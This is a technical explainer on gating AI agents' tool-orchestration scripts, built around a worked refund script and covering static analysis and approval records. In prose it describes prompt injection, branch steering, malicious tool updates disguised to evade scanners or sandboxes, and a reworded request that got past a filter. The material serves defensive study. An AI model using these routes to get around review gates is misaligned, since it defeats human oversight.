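# Reviewing agent-written tool-orchestration scripts before they run

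## What a tool-orchestration script is and where a check can be placed

An AI agent is a language model connected to software that lets it act, for instance by searching a database, sending an email or making a payment. Each such ability is a *tool*. The model uses a tool by producing a structured request, a *tool call*, which ordinary software carries out. Early agents requested one or a few calls at a time. In many agents now, the model writes a short program that calls several tools and processes their results in code, and a runtime executes the program. Such a program is a *tool-orchestration script*, or script for short. *Programmatic tool calling* means running scripts so that only the final output returns to the model.

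Organisations often check an agent's proposed actions before they take effect, especially where the agent can move money or delete things. When the agent proposes a script instead of a single call, the reviewer has to judge a program rather than one concrete action, often before anyone has seen the data it will work on.

### From single calls to a script

OpenAI's developer guide *Function calling* divides the ordinary tool-calling loop into five steps. The application sends the model a task and a list of tools. The model returns a tool call, which consists of a tool's name and its arguments. The application runs the matching code, sends the output back in a second request, and receives either a final answer or more calls. The guide includes issuing refunds among its examples of what a tool might do.

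Suppose a shop suspects it charged some customers twice in November. In the loop, the model requests the month's charges, reads them, finds a duplicate, requests a refund, reads the confirmation, requests an email to the customer, and moves on to the next duplicate. If the month has 1,200 charges and 40 duplicates, the job takes 81 calls: one to list the charges, 40 refunds and 40 emails. The model can shorten the sequence by bundling several calls into one response, but every charge still passes through its *context*, the text available to it while it works.

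The *refund script* does the same job in seven lines of Python:

```python
charges = await list_charges(month="2026-11")
keys = [(c["customer"], c["amount"]) for c in charges]
duplicates = [c for i, c in enumerate(charges) if keys[i] in keys[:i]]
for c in duplicates:
    await issue_refund(charge=c["id"], amount=c["amount"])
    await send_email(to=c["email"], text=f"We refunded {c['amount']}.")
print(len(duplicates), "duplicates refunded")
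```

Line 1 fetches the charges; `await` makes the program wait for the result. Line 2 reduces each charge to a pair, the customer and the amount. Line 3 keeps every charge whose pair appeared earlier in the list, which is the script's only test for a duplicate. Line 4 starts a loop over those charges. For each one, line 5 refunds the charge and line 6 writes to the customer. Line 7 prints a count, which is the only output the model will receive.

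Lines 1, 5 and 6 are the script's *call sites*, the places where its text calls a tool. A call site can run any number of times. Line 5 runs 40 times on the November data and would not run at all in a month without duplicates. Only lines 5 and 6 have *effects*, which are changes or disclosures to anything outside the script.

The approach goes back to CodeAct, a framework in which Wang, Chen and colleagues (2024), in *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents*, had models act by writing executable Python, so that one action could loop over all inputs. Li, He and colleagues (2026), in *ProgAgent*, give the difference from the ordinary loop an exact form. With direct calls, each turn adds two things to the context:

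new context = old context + call + result

With a script, the results drop out:

new context = old context + program + printed output

The script keeps *intermediate data* in variables, and the model never reads it. This is a major reason to use a script. Anthropic's *Introducing advanced tool use on the Claude Developer Platform* describes a budget check on 20 employees in which more than 2,000 expense lines would otherwise enter the context. The script cuts 200 kilobytes of raw data to about one kilobyte of results, and it also saves time. Accuracy may also fall less as the data grows. When Li and colleagues enlarged the databases behind their tasks, the share of tasks that DeepSeek V4 Pro solved at least once in eight attempts fell from 95% to 42% with direct calls but stayed above 90% with programs. However, the comparison is biased toward programs, because the team had kept only tasks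 that the same model sometimes solved by program.

### One run, step by step

OpenAI's *Programmatic Tool Calling* documents a runtime that takes JavaScript, so the refund script would need translating first. The run would then go like this:

1. The application sends the task and the definitions of the three tools. Each definition has a field, `allowed_callers`, in which the developer states whether programs may call the tool.
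2. The model writes the program, which OpenAI's service returns as a `program` item containing the code and an identifier.
3. OpenAI starts the code in a fresh *sandbox*, an environment that limits what running code can reach. This one has no direct network access, no general file system and no way to install packages. The program can affect outside systems only through the tools that the developer enabled.
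4. Execution reaches `list_charges` and pauses. The service sends the developer's application a `function_call` item with the tool's name, its arguments and a `caller` field that points back to the program.
5. The application queries the payment system itself and returns the 1,200 charges as a `function_call_output`. It copies the `caller` field unchanged, so that the service resumes the right program.
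6. The program picks out the duplicates and pauses again at the first refund. This time the `function_call` item contains an actual charge number and an actual amount. The same exchange follows for each refund and each email.
7. The service issues a `program_output` item with the text "40 duplicates refunded". The model reads that line and writes its reply to the user.

In OpenAI's sample response, the program's text and its first function calls arrive together, so the application first sees the script when it is already running. This does no harm for tools that the application runs itself, since they do nothing until the application answers. But a tool that OpenAI hosts could have acted before the application has a chance to review the script.

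Anthropic's version works in much the same way. According to *Programmatic tool calling*, the model writes Python, Anthropic runs it in a container, and the script pauses at each tool call until the developer supplies the result. Results arrive as strings, so the refund script would also have to parse the list of charges. Later requests can reuse the container and its state, whereas OpenAI's runtime starts empty each time.

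Cloudflare, which sells network and hosting services, calls the pattern Code Mode. Varda and Pai's *Code Mode* describes running each script in a new isolate, a lightweight, separate instance of the JavaScript engine V8 that starts in milliseconds. The isolate has no internet access. It contains ready-made objects that represent the connected services, while the access keys stay outside, where generated code cannot leak them. The larger difference from OpenAI and Anthropic is that Cloudflare's runtime itself intercepts every call before it executes and applies the developer's rules on approval and logging, according to Cloudflare's *How Code Mode works*. OpenAI and Anthropic pass the call to the developer's application and leave it to apply such rules.

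The pattern is spreading among coding agents, although parts of it are still provisional. Cloudflare's *Code Mode* was labeled "experimental" in June 2026. The coding agent Pi adopted the approach in version 1.0 (Ronacher, *What is Codemode*, 2026). InfoQ's *Claude Code Adds Experimental Code Mode to Orchestrate Tool Calls with JavaScript* (2026) reports that Anthropic's coding agent also adopted it, and that the way the agent's automatic reviewer treats calls inside a script changed.

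The number of calls in a typical script is less clear. Mak, Suresh and colleagues (2026) ran agents on two benchmarks of office work for *Is Bash All You Need?* and found only about two tool calls per program. A script with 81 calls is therefore probably larger than most. It also repeats one operation over many items, which is the kind of job Anthropic recommends scripts for.

### What changes for the reviewer

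In the ordinary loop, a *permission prompt* (a request that a person approve one action before it runs) can show the charge, the amount and the customer. The model has also read the charges by then, so it might recognize two identical payments a minute apart as purchases of two concert tickets and leave them alone.

The refund script removes both chances. One decision to run it covers 80 effects, and at that point neither the model nor the reviewer has seen any of the charges. The script has `c["amount"]` where the prompt would have shown an actual amount. Line 3 will refund the second concert ticket because its customer and amount match those of the first.

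Scripts also make existing review tools less effective. *DADL* (Dunkel, 2026) describes a system that gives a model access to more than 1,800 tools through two tools, one that searches the catalogue and one that executes a script. Software that used to compare each call with a fixed schema now has to analyse code. Rules that allow or forbid tools by name can't distinguish between the tools a script calls if they are applied outside the runtime, where only the execution tool's name is visible. Dunkel accepts these as real drawbacks of the design.

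A script does, however, give some protection against *prompt injection*, in which attackers plant instructions in data that an agent reads. A sentence hidden in the description of a charge might redirect a model that reads it, but it has no effect on a loop that only compares customers and amounts. The protection is partial because the model may have read the planted text before it wrote the script, or may read it in the printed output. Anthropic also warns of a risk when a script runs the contents of a tool result as code.

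One response is to keep effects out of scripts. OpenAI advises using direct calls by default for writes and for anything that needs approval, to preserve "a clear authorization boundary". The refund script would then end after line 3 and print the duplicates, and the model would request 80 refunds and emails directly. Cloudflare's *AI SDK integration* states that the company's simpler integration applies the same policy by excluding tools that need approval from scripts. The policy is sound for a handful of writes, but for 80 it brings back most of the calls that the script was meant to replace. Vendors also don't follow it everywhere. Anthropic reports that Claude for Excel uses programmatic tool calling to modify spreadsheets with thousands of rows, and Cloudflare's fuller runtime allows scripts to use tools that need approval. Somebody therefore still has to decide whether to let scripts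 with effects run.

### Three places for a gate

A *gate* is a check that must pass before a script, or one call in it, may run. The term also covers a check at the end of a run if the run's effects are not final until the check passes.

A check can run before the script starts. *Governance by Construction for Generalist Agents* (2026) describes a system that scans model-generated code for tool invocations and, if it finds a tool on the sensitive list, holds the script until someone approves it. For the refund script, the reviewer makes one decision before any balance is corrected or any email is sent, so blocking the script leaves nothing to undo. But the reviewer sees only the script's seven lines, which don't show the number of refunds, the total amount, or the recipients.

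A check can also run at each call. In Dunkel's system, the runtime checks every call against the user's role and a label on the tool (read, write, admin or dangerous) before sending the request. On OpenAI's runtime, the natural place for this check is the developer's application, and OpenAI tells developers to verify arguments and permissions there even when the call comes from a program. At this point the arguments have actual values, so a rule such as "no refund above 500 dollars" is easier to enforce than it was before the script ran, when the amount was only the expression `c["amount"]`.

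A check at this position applies to one call at a time and doesn't cover the run as a whole. The fortieth refund looks much like the first, so the check will pass all 40 unless it also keeps a running total. If it stops the thirtieth refund, 29 customers already have their money. On Cloudflare's runtime, rejecting an action ends the run but does not undo earlier actions. Human approval also takes time. Anthropic's container stops waiting for a result after about four minutes, while Cloudflare's runtime records how far the script got and runs it again once the answer comes.

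The last place for a check is after the run, when the reviewer can see everything that happened and either keep it or reverse it. Wu, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Shall We Approve?*, built such a gate for the shell commands of coding agents. Their system takes a snapshot of the agent's container, runs the command inside it with the network off, gives an AI model a report of the observed effects, and then keeps the new state or restores the old one. The network is off because a rollback can only reverse effects inside the container.

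Refunds and emails are meant to reach the customer. For such cases, Cloudflare offers a rollback that goes back through the completed calls and runs a reversing action wherever the developer has written one. But reversing a refund would mean charging the customer again, and an email can't be reversed once the customer has read it. A check after the run is therefore of little use for the refund script unless someone first finds a way to hold back the refunds and emails.

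### What a gate is meant to stop

Scripts that run in a sandbox still need a gate, because the sandbox keeps a script from bypassing its tools but doesn't check whether it uses them well. OpenAI's and Cloudflare's runtimes both cut scripts off from the open internet by default, but the refund script would run unobstructed in either one because the developer connected `issue_refund` on purpose.

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* distinguishes four reasons why an agent might take a dangerous action, and each has a version in the shop:

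- **Overeager help.** The agent understands the goal and goes further than the user would approve. The user asked which customers had paid twice, and the script refunds them. Anthropic's internal log has real cases of this kind, including an agent that deleted remote branches of a code repository after misreading an instruction.
- **Honest mistakes.** The agent is wrong about what its action will touch. The concert tickets belong here, and so would a `list_charges` that returns every branch's charges when the model assumed it covered one.
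- **Prompt injection.** A support ticket that the agent read before writing the script contains a planted sentence, and line 6 now sends a copy of each email to a stranger.
- **A misaligned model.** The model pursues a goal of its own and writes the script to serve it, perhaps by making a harmful line look routine.

Anthropic concludes that the defence in all four cases is to block the action, so a gate need not establish why a script is harmful. But the causes differ in how much they leave for a reviewer to find. The extra recipient in line 6 is visible in the script's text, while the concert tickets are in the data.

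Every gate makes mistakes, and two rates measure them. The *false positive rate* is the share of harmless actions the gate blocks. The *false negative rate* is the share of harmful actions it lets through. Suppose 1,000 scripts reach a gate, 980 of them harmless and 20 harmful. If the gate blocks 49 of the harmless ones, its false positive rate is 49/980, or 5%. If it lets 4 of the harmful ones through, its false negative rate is 4/20, or 20%. The gate has blocked 65 scripts, 49 harmless and 16 harmful. Because harmful scripts are rare, about three out of four blocks were mistaken, even though the gate passes 95% of harmless scripts.

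Both rates also depend on what counts as one action. If a gate wrongly blocks 1% of harmless calls and its errors are independent, a harmless script that makes 80 refund and email calls has about a 55% chance (1 − 0.99⁸⁰) of at least one wrong block. The errors probably aren't independent, because all 80 calls come from two call sites and look alike, so a gate that passes one will tend to pass the rest. For the same reason, a gate that misses the first bad refund in a harmful script will probably miss the others too.

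## What a script's text shows when its data is still unseen

A reviewer who reads the refund script before it runs has to judge two lines that have effects, instead of 80 calls. How much this helps depends on how much the reviewer can tell from those lines alone and how much is determined by the November charges.

### Five questions for each call site

A reviewer can ask the same five things about every call site: which tool it calls, with which arguments, how many times, under which branch (the conditions under which execution reaches the line), and what the tool itself sets off once the call arrives. The refund script's text gives these answers:

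| | Line 1, `list_charges` | Line 5, `issue_refund` | Line 6, `send_email` |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tool | fixed | fixed | fixed |
| Arguments | fixed: November 2026 | charge number and amount come from the data | address and amount come from the data, the wording is fixed |
| Number of calls | one | one per duplicate | one per successful refund |
| Branch | always runs | only for a charge whose customer and amount appeared earlier in the list | only after line 5 returns without an error |
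| What the tool sets off | not in the text | not in the text | not in the text |

The top row is fixed only because the script writes out its tools' names. A script could instead pick a tool using a value it has just fetched, as in `tools[c["action"]](c["id"])`, and then the answer in that row would depend on the data too.

The script's text gives a formula for the number of calls. If the list has *n* charges with *k* different pairs of customer and amount, line 3 selects *n* − *k* of them. In November that is 1,200 − 1,160 = 40. Suppose the shop also sells to people without an account and leaves their customer field empty. If four of them each buy a 20-dollar ticket, their pairs are identical, so the script refunds three of them. If 3,001 do, the same seven lines refund 3,000.

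The text does fix some relations between values that nobody has seen yet. Line 5 takes the charge number and amount from one record, and line 6 takes the address from the same record. So the script never refunds one charge at another charge's amount, and a reviewer could easily spot a version with `amount=2*c["amount"]` or a stranger's address in line 6. Data-flow analysis, the subject of the next section, derives these relations automatically.

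Anyone who can influence the data can influence which branch of the script runs. *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) distinguishes two properties of an approved plan. *Control-flow integrity* means that every action the agent takes belongs to the plan. *Data-flow integrity* means that untrusted data can neither choose which approved branch runs nor set an action's critical arguments. The refund script has only the first property. A customer who buys the same voucher twice, spends both and waits for the monthly clean-up gets one of them free, without planting any instructions in the data.

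*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) reports the same weakness in agents that operate a computer through its screen. Each plan was complete before the agent looked at any untrusted content, yet a fake button could still steer a run onto a dangerous path that the plan allowed. Roughly half the steps in those plans were fallbacks that a given run never used, but a reviewer would still have to judge them.

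The bottom row of the table needs information from outside the script, such as a declaration by whoever made the tool. In *Small agents should know what their tools do*, Kovalenko and Redchych (2026) built a simulated office and shop where every tool has one of four declared effects: pure (it only computes), read, write or destructive. Refunds and emails count as destructive because they can't be undone. The resources each tool touches are also declared, as a pattern over its arguments, and any argument unknown at the time of the analysis becomes a wildcard. For line 5, the result would be "changes some charge, possibly any charge", which doesn't show whether the script issues three refunds or three thousand.

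The accuracy of a declaration also depends on whoever writes it. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard through which servers offer tools to agents, has similar labels, but they are only advisory under its specification. Kovalenko and Redchych cite a census of 98,291 tools, which found that the labels were common but too coarse to show what a call does.

### What Rice's theorem rules out

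*Static analysis* means deriving facts about a program from its text without running it. In 1953, Henry Gordon Rice published a theorem that limits what static analysis can achieve. If some programs have a property of behaviour, such as "issues a refund", and others lack it, no algorithm can correctly tell for every program whether the program has that property. The theorem applies to languages that can express any computation, including Python and JavaScript, and assumes a machine with unlimited time and memory.

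Møller and Schwartzbach (2025), in *Static Program Analysis*, show how such results follow from the halting problem. Alan Turing had proved that no algorithm can tell, for every program, whether it will ever stop. Suppose somebody had a perfect checker for refunds. Take any program P that calls no tools, and put it in front of one:

```python
run(P)
await issue_refund(charge="ch_1", amount=20)
```

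This script issues a refund if and only if P stops. The checker would therefore solve the halting problem, so it can't exist. Rice's theorem concerns the results that programs return. *No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard* (Amer, Kinczel and Long, 2026) restates it for the actions that programs perform. A gate needs this version because a program can make a harmful call without ever returning anything.

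Even a short, readable program can be hard to judge from its text. Pérez-Acle (2026), in *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program*, describes a program that goes through the even numbers above 2 and performs a forbidden action at the first one that is not the sum of two primes. The program is harmless exactly if Goldbach's conjecture is true, and the conjecture was still open when the paper appeared in November 2026. If the program is harmful, running it long enough will prove it, but no amount of running will prove that it is harmless.

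Admitting only programs that are certain to finish is not enough to escape the theorem. Møller and Schwartzbach prove that no analysis can decide whether a program may fail on some input, even if the analysis only has to be right about programs that always halt. A time limit makes the question decidable for a given input, because the checker can run the program until the limit. But Pérez-Acle proves that a checker that is always right must, for some programs, run for about as long as the limit.

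A useful gate is still possible, because it doesn't have to classify every program. Møller and Schwartzbach describe analysers that return either "yes, definitely" or "maybe", and a gate can treat "maybe" as a refusal. The Linux kernel does this with eBPF programs, which are small extensions that it loads only if its verifier can prove them safe. In general, according to Pérez-Acle, a gate needs a checkable list that contains every program it must admit and none that it must refuse. The shop's list might contain all scripts that write out their tool names, never run data as code, and loop only over lists they have fetched. It would include the refund script but not the Goldbach program.

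Amer and colleagues prove that, when no algorithm can decide a policy, any guard that blocks every forbidden output also blocks infinitely many permitted ones. These false positives may still be rare in practice, because infinitely many possible programs may include very few that an agent ever writes. Amer and colleagues also show that, for any fixed mix of outputs, there is a guard that blocks everything forbidden and wrongly blocks as rarely as one likes, though there is no general method for building it.

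Pérez-Acle offers some evidence that hard cases are rare. In a sample of 2.2 million random programs, 1.6% were unsafe, and a test that monitored the first 128 steps caught all of them. These percentages don't transfer to agent-written scripts, because random sequences of at most 24 instructions are a poor model of what an agent writes. Still, the results suggest that hard cases come mostly from someone trying to defeat the checker. A misaligned model might write such a script, but a gate that rejects any script it can't show to be safe would reject that one too.

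The main obstacle to reviewing the refund script is missing data rather than Rice's theorem. The script finishes on any list of charges, and its text is enough to show that it can issue more than 50 refunds on some data. The reviewer wants to know whether it will do so on November's data, which the text doesn't contain. Pérez-Acle's gatekeeper has the opposite problem, because it has all the information it needs but lacks the computation to reach an answer.

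The model can, however, move some answers from the data into the text. It could add two lines after line 3:

```python
if len(duplicates) > 50 or any(c["amount"] > 40 for c in duplicates):
    raise ValueError("more or larger refunds than expected")
```

Now the script will request at most 50 refunds of at most 40 dollars each, or 2,000 dollars in total, whatever the payment system returns. A gate could reject scripts that lack such limits. The script would still refund the second concert ticket if it cost less than 40 dollars.

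### When data becomes code or instructions

Everything the text guarantees about the refund script holds only if the script never runs its data as instructions. Under that condition, data can fill in an address or decide whether a line runs, but it can't add a line. Two common constructions remove that guarantee.

A script can run data as code. Anthropic's runtime returns the charges as a string, which the script can parse with `json.loads`, which only builds the list. `eval` often produces the same list, but it runs the string as Python, so a compromised payment server could return code in place of the charges. If the script contains even one `eval`, all five answers depend on the data, and the only limit left is the set of tools that the sandbox offers, which in the shop allows any refund and any email. *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution* (Felendler, Gandhi and colleagues, 2026)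 counts this among sixteen classes of attack on agents that call MCP tools through code.

When a script fails, the model typically reads the error message, writes a corrected script and runs it. An attacker who controls the error message can therefore influence the second script without touching the first. Approval of the first script doesn't cover the second, so a gate has to check every new version, however small the correction looks.

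The other construction hands data to a model that can act. Suppose line 6 passed the customer's address and the note on the charge to a support agent that could issue refunds itself. In the script's text, this would still be one call with one string argument. But the note might contain a request to refund last year's orders too, and the agent might comply.

*When Tool Outputs Become Commands* (2026) distinguishes between tool output that fills in an action the user wanted and tool output that adds a new one. If a user asks an agent to find the quarterly report and send it to Alice, the search result may supply the file's name, but an instruction in that result to send a copy to somebody else would add an action. In an ordinary script, data can only fill in actions, because every possible action has its own call site. If the script contains an agent, data can also add actions.

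Reading the script more carefully doesn't help much at that point. *Prompt Flow Integrity to Prevent Privilege Escalation in LLM Agents* (2025) notes that program code determines exactly where data flows in conventional software, whereas in a language model every input can influence the output to some extent. Amer and colleagues prove that no algorithm can decide which messages are harmful to a recipient that carries out any instructions exactly. They add that an agent that reads documents isn't necessarily such a recipient, so the difficulty with real agents is more that their behavior is unpredictable than that the problem is provably undecidable.

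A gate can still check what the inner agent tries to do. The system in *When Tool Outputs Become Commands* lets the agent read the untrusted content, then checks each resulting call against the user's request. Attacks succeeded in at most 0.63% of attempts in its four main test settings. An inner model without tools also poses less risk. If it only answers whether a note mentions a complaint, a planted sentence can change the answer and therefore which branch the script takes, but can't add an action to the script.

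### Approvals that leave out effects

The shop's reviewer may also know too little about what a tool sets off. In *Agent Approval Laundering*, Zhang, Xia and colleagues (2026) measured how often this happens in coding agents. Their first example is an agent that asked permission to install a software project's packages. The approval record named the command exactly, but the installation also ran a script that the project had registered to run during installation, and the script wrote a file that the record did not mention. They use the term *approval laundering* for cases where a record truthfully names the approved action but omits effects of the workflow that the action started. This can happen without an attacker.

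They define the property that such a record lacks. Let Rep(p) be the set of effects that the record p lists. The approved action can unfold in different ways, and each way is a trace τ with its own set of effects, Eff(τ). The *closure* C is the set of all traces that the action can produce, given the files, tools and starting state at the moment of the decision. An approval is *closure-bound* if

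Eff(τ) ⊆ Rep(p) for every τ in C

Under this condition, a record may be an *over-approximation*, listing everything a program might do, including some effects that never occur, but it may not leave out an effect that does occur. A single run with an unlisted effect therefore shows that an approval was not closure-bound, but a run without one doesn't show that it was.

Zhang and colleagues derive a short lemma from this setting. If two runs have identical records but one should be allowed and the other blocked, no policy that decides from the record alone can be certain to get both right. The policy receives the same input both times, so it allows both runs with the same probability, which would have to be 1 to always allow the first and 0 to always block the second. Randomizing the decision only shifts errors from one run to the other.

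The lemma implies that no reviewer, whether a program, an AI model or a person, can be certain to approve the refund script in the month with three refunds and block it in the month with three thousand if they see only its seven lines. The reviewer can reject the script in both months, limit what it may do, or obtain information that differs between the two months. Showing an AI reviewer the current state of a code repository is an example of the last option.

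Zhang and colleagues measured how often approval records omit effects by comparing 111 records with what the approved actions went on to do. They sorted effects into six classes: starting a process, changing files, changing environment settings, using the network, using a container, and using an MCP tool. They then counted the records that omitted at least one class, first using only what the record stated, then adding general knowledge of the command (for example, that installing packages usually writes files), and finally adding the project's own configuration files.

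| Records | Record alone | With knowledge of the command | With project files too |
|---|---|---|---|
| 60 from purpose-built tests | 30 | 15 | 13 |
| 40 from a control across five coding agents | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| 11 from public software projects | 10 | 2 | 0 |
| All 111 | 40 | 17 | 13 |

The total of 40 in 111 depends on how many tests and controls the team chose to include, so it can't be used to estimate how common the problem is. The public projects are more realistic, but their 11 runs covered only eight cases, which the team had picked because their files contained mechanisms of this kind. The figures do show how much each layer of information recovers. Knowing the command resolved 23 of the 40 incomplete records, and the project files resolved four more. The remaining 13 all came from the purpose-built tests.

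MCP calls differed from the rest. Six of the 14 MCP records omitted an effect, and general knowledge of the command helped with none of them, because a reviewer can't learn anything about the server just from knowing that a call uses MCP. The configuration files resolved two of the six. In both, an agent had called a documentation tool, and a 123-byte file showed that the call would go over the network.

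The figures in the last column come from a retrospective analysis. The team tested whether software could fill the gaps in advance on 18 workflows from 18 projects not used earlier. The software read each project's files and made a final prediction before anything ran. Averaged over the 17 workflows that ran, the predictions included 92.6% of the effects that occurred (recall), and 94.1% of the predicted effects occurred (precision). Predictions based on the command alone had 77.0% recall at the same precision.

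The team then wrote the predictions into the approval record before the decision. This *effect-bound record* contains the action, the predicted effects, the files behind each prediction and a *hash* of each file, which is a short fingerprint that changes if the file does. The actual outcome can be added later, but it can't change what the record listed at approval. Across the 17 workflows, effect-bound records left out three effects, all of them file changes, while records based on the command alone left out ten.

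The result is promising, but the test was small, and an earlier version of the software had a recall of only 69.4% on a different set of real projects. The records would give the person approving more information about each action, but they were little help in deciding when to ask and would hardly reduce the number of requests. A policy built on them requested an extra approval in 17 of the 18 cases, including eight of the nine negative or low-risk controls. In nine of the 17 workflows that ran, nothing happened beyond what the simpler record had already listed.

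### Which of these results apply to scripts

Zhang and colleagues studied single commands and tool calls in coding agents, not scripts that call many tools. They argue that the approach extends to any system that has a vocabulary of effects, sources that reveal in advance how an action will unfold, evidence of what started, and evidence of what happened.

The lemma carries over unchanged because nothing in its proof is specific to coding. The definition of a closure-bound approval also carries over, but the six classes are too coarse for the shop. They don't distinguish a run with three refunds from one with three thousand, or an email to the customer from an email to a stranger. The paper allows for finer labels that include destinations and arguments, and a shop would need those as well as counts and totals.

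The measured recall and precision don't carry over to scripts like the refund script. The prediction software worked because it could read the relevant information in files before the decision. A package's installation script is on the disk, or at least the project's files refer to it. For the refund script, the equivalent information is the list of November charges in the payment system, plus whatever the payment company's servers do when a refund arrives. The charges are available only if somebody fetches them before the script runs. A preview does this and lists the concrete effects before any of them happens. The company's server code is usually not available at all.

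The idea of an effect-bound record is still useful. An approval of the refund script could include "up to 50 refunds of up to 40 dollars, one email for each" instead of storing only the code. A runtime could then enforce those limits, and an auditor could later compare them with what happened. With the two lines added above, the script's text alone would justify the limits on the refunds.

### When the tool changes after the review

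If the reviewer finds out exactly what `issue_refund` sets off, that knowledge applies only to the version of the tool that existed at the time. In *Beyond Prompt Injection*, Kan, Luo and colleagues (2026) examined seven agent frameworks, including Claude Code, Codex CLI and Gemini CLI, and found that in all of them, permission for a tool could persist after the code behind it had changed. They call this the *tool-update gap*.

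To test this, they installed a harmless tool that tidies up text and then updated it. The new version kept the same name, description and input format, and it still tidied text. But it also did one of three things the user had not asked for: it sent a file of dummy passwords to a test server, placed an order through a test service, or overwrote a research note. In the main experiment, the hidden action succeeded in 100% of tasks, and the user received the correct text in 99.6%. Across all experiments, including those with other models and tools, the figures were 97.6% and 95.9%.

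For comparison, the team tried updates that put instructions in the tool's description and relied on the model to follow them. These succeeded in only 20.2% of tasks. The hidden code succeeded more often because it didn't depend on the model following instructions. Some frameworks asked for confirmation before each call, but this made no difference because the confirmation covered only the call, not the code it would run.

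A script is exposed in the same way, and one approval covers more calls. If a new version of `issue_refund` also copied customer details to a stranger, line 5 would look the same and any analysis of the script would give the same result, but the November run would call the new code 40 times.

Kan and colleagues tested several defences, and each had a serious drawback:

- **Reviewing the code of each update.** An AI-based scanner rejected 98.3% of the malicious updates while their code was readable. After the team had disguised the code with PyArmor, a commercial tool, the attack succeeded in 85.0% of tasks despite the review.
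- **Limiting how much a file may change.** Refusing every change stops attacks, but it also stops repairs until somebody approves the new version. A looser limit that still blocked all three malicious updates rejected 22 of 40 legitimate ones.
- **Watching the tool run in a sandbox.** This caught all 30 malicious runs and raised no false alarm in 30 harmless ones. However, one variant recognised the sandbox and behaved well until it was outside.

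They conclude that an approval should apply to the code somebody reviewed, not to the tool's name. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026) describes a way to do this. A registry stores a certificate for each tool, and the system recomputes the tool's hashes at every call. If they no longer match, it aborts before interpreting the arguments. This ensures that the code hasn't changed since the review, but not that the review was right. Kan and colleagues therefore also want the runtime to block any operation outside a tool's declared function.

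A further limit is that hashes work only for code the shop can read. If the payment company runs `issue_refund` on its own servers, the shop can hash the tool's description and any code on the shop's side, but the company can change what a refund triggers without changing either. The shop then has to rely on the company's documentation and whatever effects it can observe.

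## Checking tool calls and data flows by static analysis

Static analysis can automate some checks of a script's call sites. The simplest check uses only the names of the tools. More thorough checks trace which data can reach which tool and compare the result with a written policy.

### Scanning for tool names

The simplest kind of gate holds a script for approval if it calls a tool on a sensitive list. *Governance by Construction for Generalist Agents* describes such a gate in CUGA, an agent developed at IBM. In the published demonstration, an attacker rewords a harmful request to get past an earlier filter, and the agent writes code that would drop a database. The gate scans the code and stops it before it runs.

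The shop would put `issue_refund` and `send_email` on the list. The refund script would then wait for approval every month, however many refunds it was about to issue, and a person would still have to decide whether to approve them. The published results give little evidence of the scan's accuracy. On a benchmark of 26 back-office tasks, CUGA's policy system raised GPT-OSS-120B's success rate from 49.2% to 82.3%, but those figures cover the whole system, and the gains explained in the paper came from other parts, such as step-by-step instructions for the agent.

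A scan for tool names can raise false alarms or miss calls. A plain text search for `issue_refund` finds a script that sets `pay = issue_refund` and later calls `pay(...)`, but it also flags a script that only mentions `issue_refund` in a comment. A search restricted to calls to `issue_refund` ignores the comment but misses the call through `pay`. To get both cases right, the scanner has to work out what each name refers to, which is also an early step in tracing data.

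### The data-flow algorithm

A data-flow analysis follows six steps:

1. Parse the text into a *syntax tree*, in which every assignment, loop and call is a node, and the body of a loop hangs below the loop. Comments drop out here.
2. Walk through the tree and collect the call sites.
3. Work out which function each call refers to, following imports and assignments such as `pay = issue_refund`.
4. Label the data that each *source* returns. A source is a call that brings data into the script, and a label states what kind of data it is.
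5. Propagate the labels. A value computed from other values receives all of their labels. Repeat this over the whole script until a pass adds nothing new.
6. Check every *sink*, which is a call that can send data out or change something. Compare the labels of its arguments with the policy.

*ACE* (2025) applies this method to agent plans written in a subset of Python. In one example, a plan loads bank details and passes them to an email tool. The details are labelled "financial" and the email tool is cleared only for "personal", so the analyser rejects the plan before anything runs.

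With sets of labels, the mathematics is short. If the script computes *y* from *x*₁, …, *x*ₙ, step 5 performs the update

labels(*y*) ← labels(*y*) ∪ labels(*x*₁) ∪ … ∪ labels(*x*ₙ)

and step 6 checks, for every call to a tool, that

labels(arguments) ⊆ clearance(tool)

The repetition in step 5 is there because of loops. This variant of the refund loop follows the pattern of another example in *ACE*:

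```python
note = ""
for c in duplicates:
    await send_email(to=c["email"], text=note)
    note = c["card"]
```

On the first pass, `note` has no label when the analyser reaches the email, because it gets the label "card" only on the last line. On the second pass, `note` carries that label into the email. In a real run, the first customer would get an empty message and the second would get the first customer's card number. An analyser that went through the loop only once would miss this.

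The repetition always ends because the analyser only adds labels, and with *v* variables and *l* labels it can make at most *v* × *l* additions, however often the loop itself runs. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) needs only one pass because its planning language doesn't let a plan reassign a variable.

### The refund script by hand

Suppose the shop declares that each record from `list_charges` has five fields (`id`, `customer`, `amount`, `email` and `card`) and gives each field a label of the same name. The name `card` never appears in the refund script.

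Parsing produces three assignments, a loop with two statements, and a print statement. The tree contains six calls, three to tools and three to the Python built-ins `enumerate`, `len` and `print`. Name resolution is easy because the script never reassigns a tool's name, although the analyser must treat `c` as a separate variable in each of lines 2, 3 and 4.

Propagation then gives these labels:

| Line | Value | Labels from its content | Labels from the conditions behind it |
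|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `charges` | all five, each on its own field | none |
| 2 | `keys` | customer, amount | none |
| 3 | `duplicates` | all five, each on its own field | customer, amount |
| 5 | charge number for the refund | id | customer, amount |
| 5 | amount of the refund | amount | customer, amount |
| 6 | address of the email | email | customer, amount |
| 6 | text of the email | amount | customer, amount |
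| 7 | printed count | none | customer, amount |

The last column is there because line 3 compares customers and amounts to decide which charges enter the list. The count and everything in the loop depend on that comparison. A second pass over the loop adds nothing because no iteration stores anything for the next one.

On line 7, the analyser needs a rule that the length of a list reveals only which items are in it. Without this rule, `len(duplicates)` would receive all five labels, and a policy that keeps card numbers away from the model would reject a script that prints the number 40.

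### A rule that labels settle and one they don't

The shop's first rule is that card numbers never reach email. Neither column for line 6 contains "card", so the script passes. The result holds for any list of charges, since the analysis never used November's data. But it relies on the shop's declaration, so if a clerk had typed a card number into the `customer` field, a script that emailed that field would pass too. *ACE* has the same limit, because its analysis can't detect leaks from a source the user failed to label.

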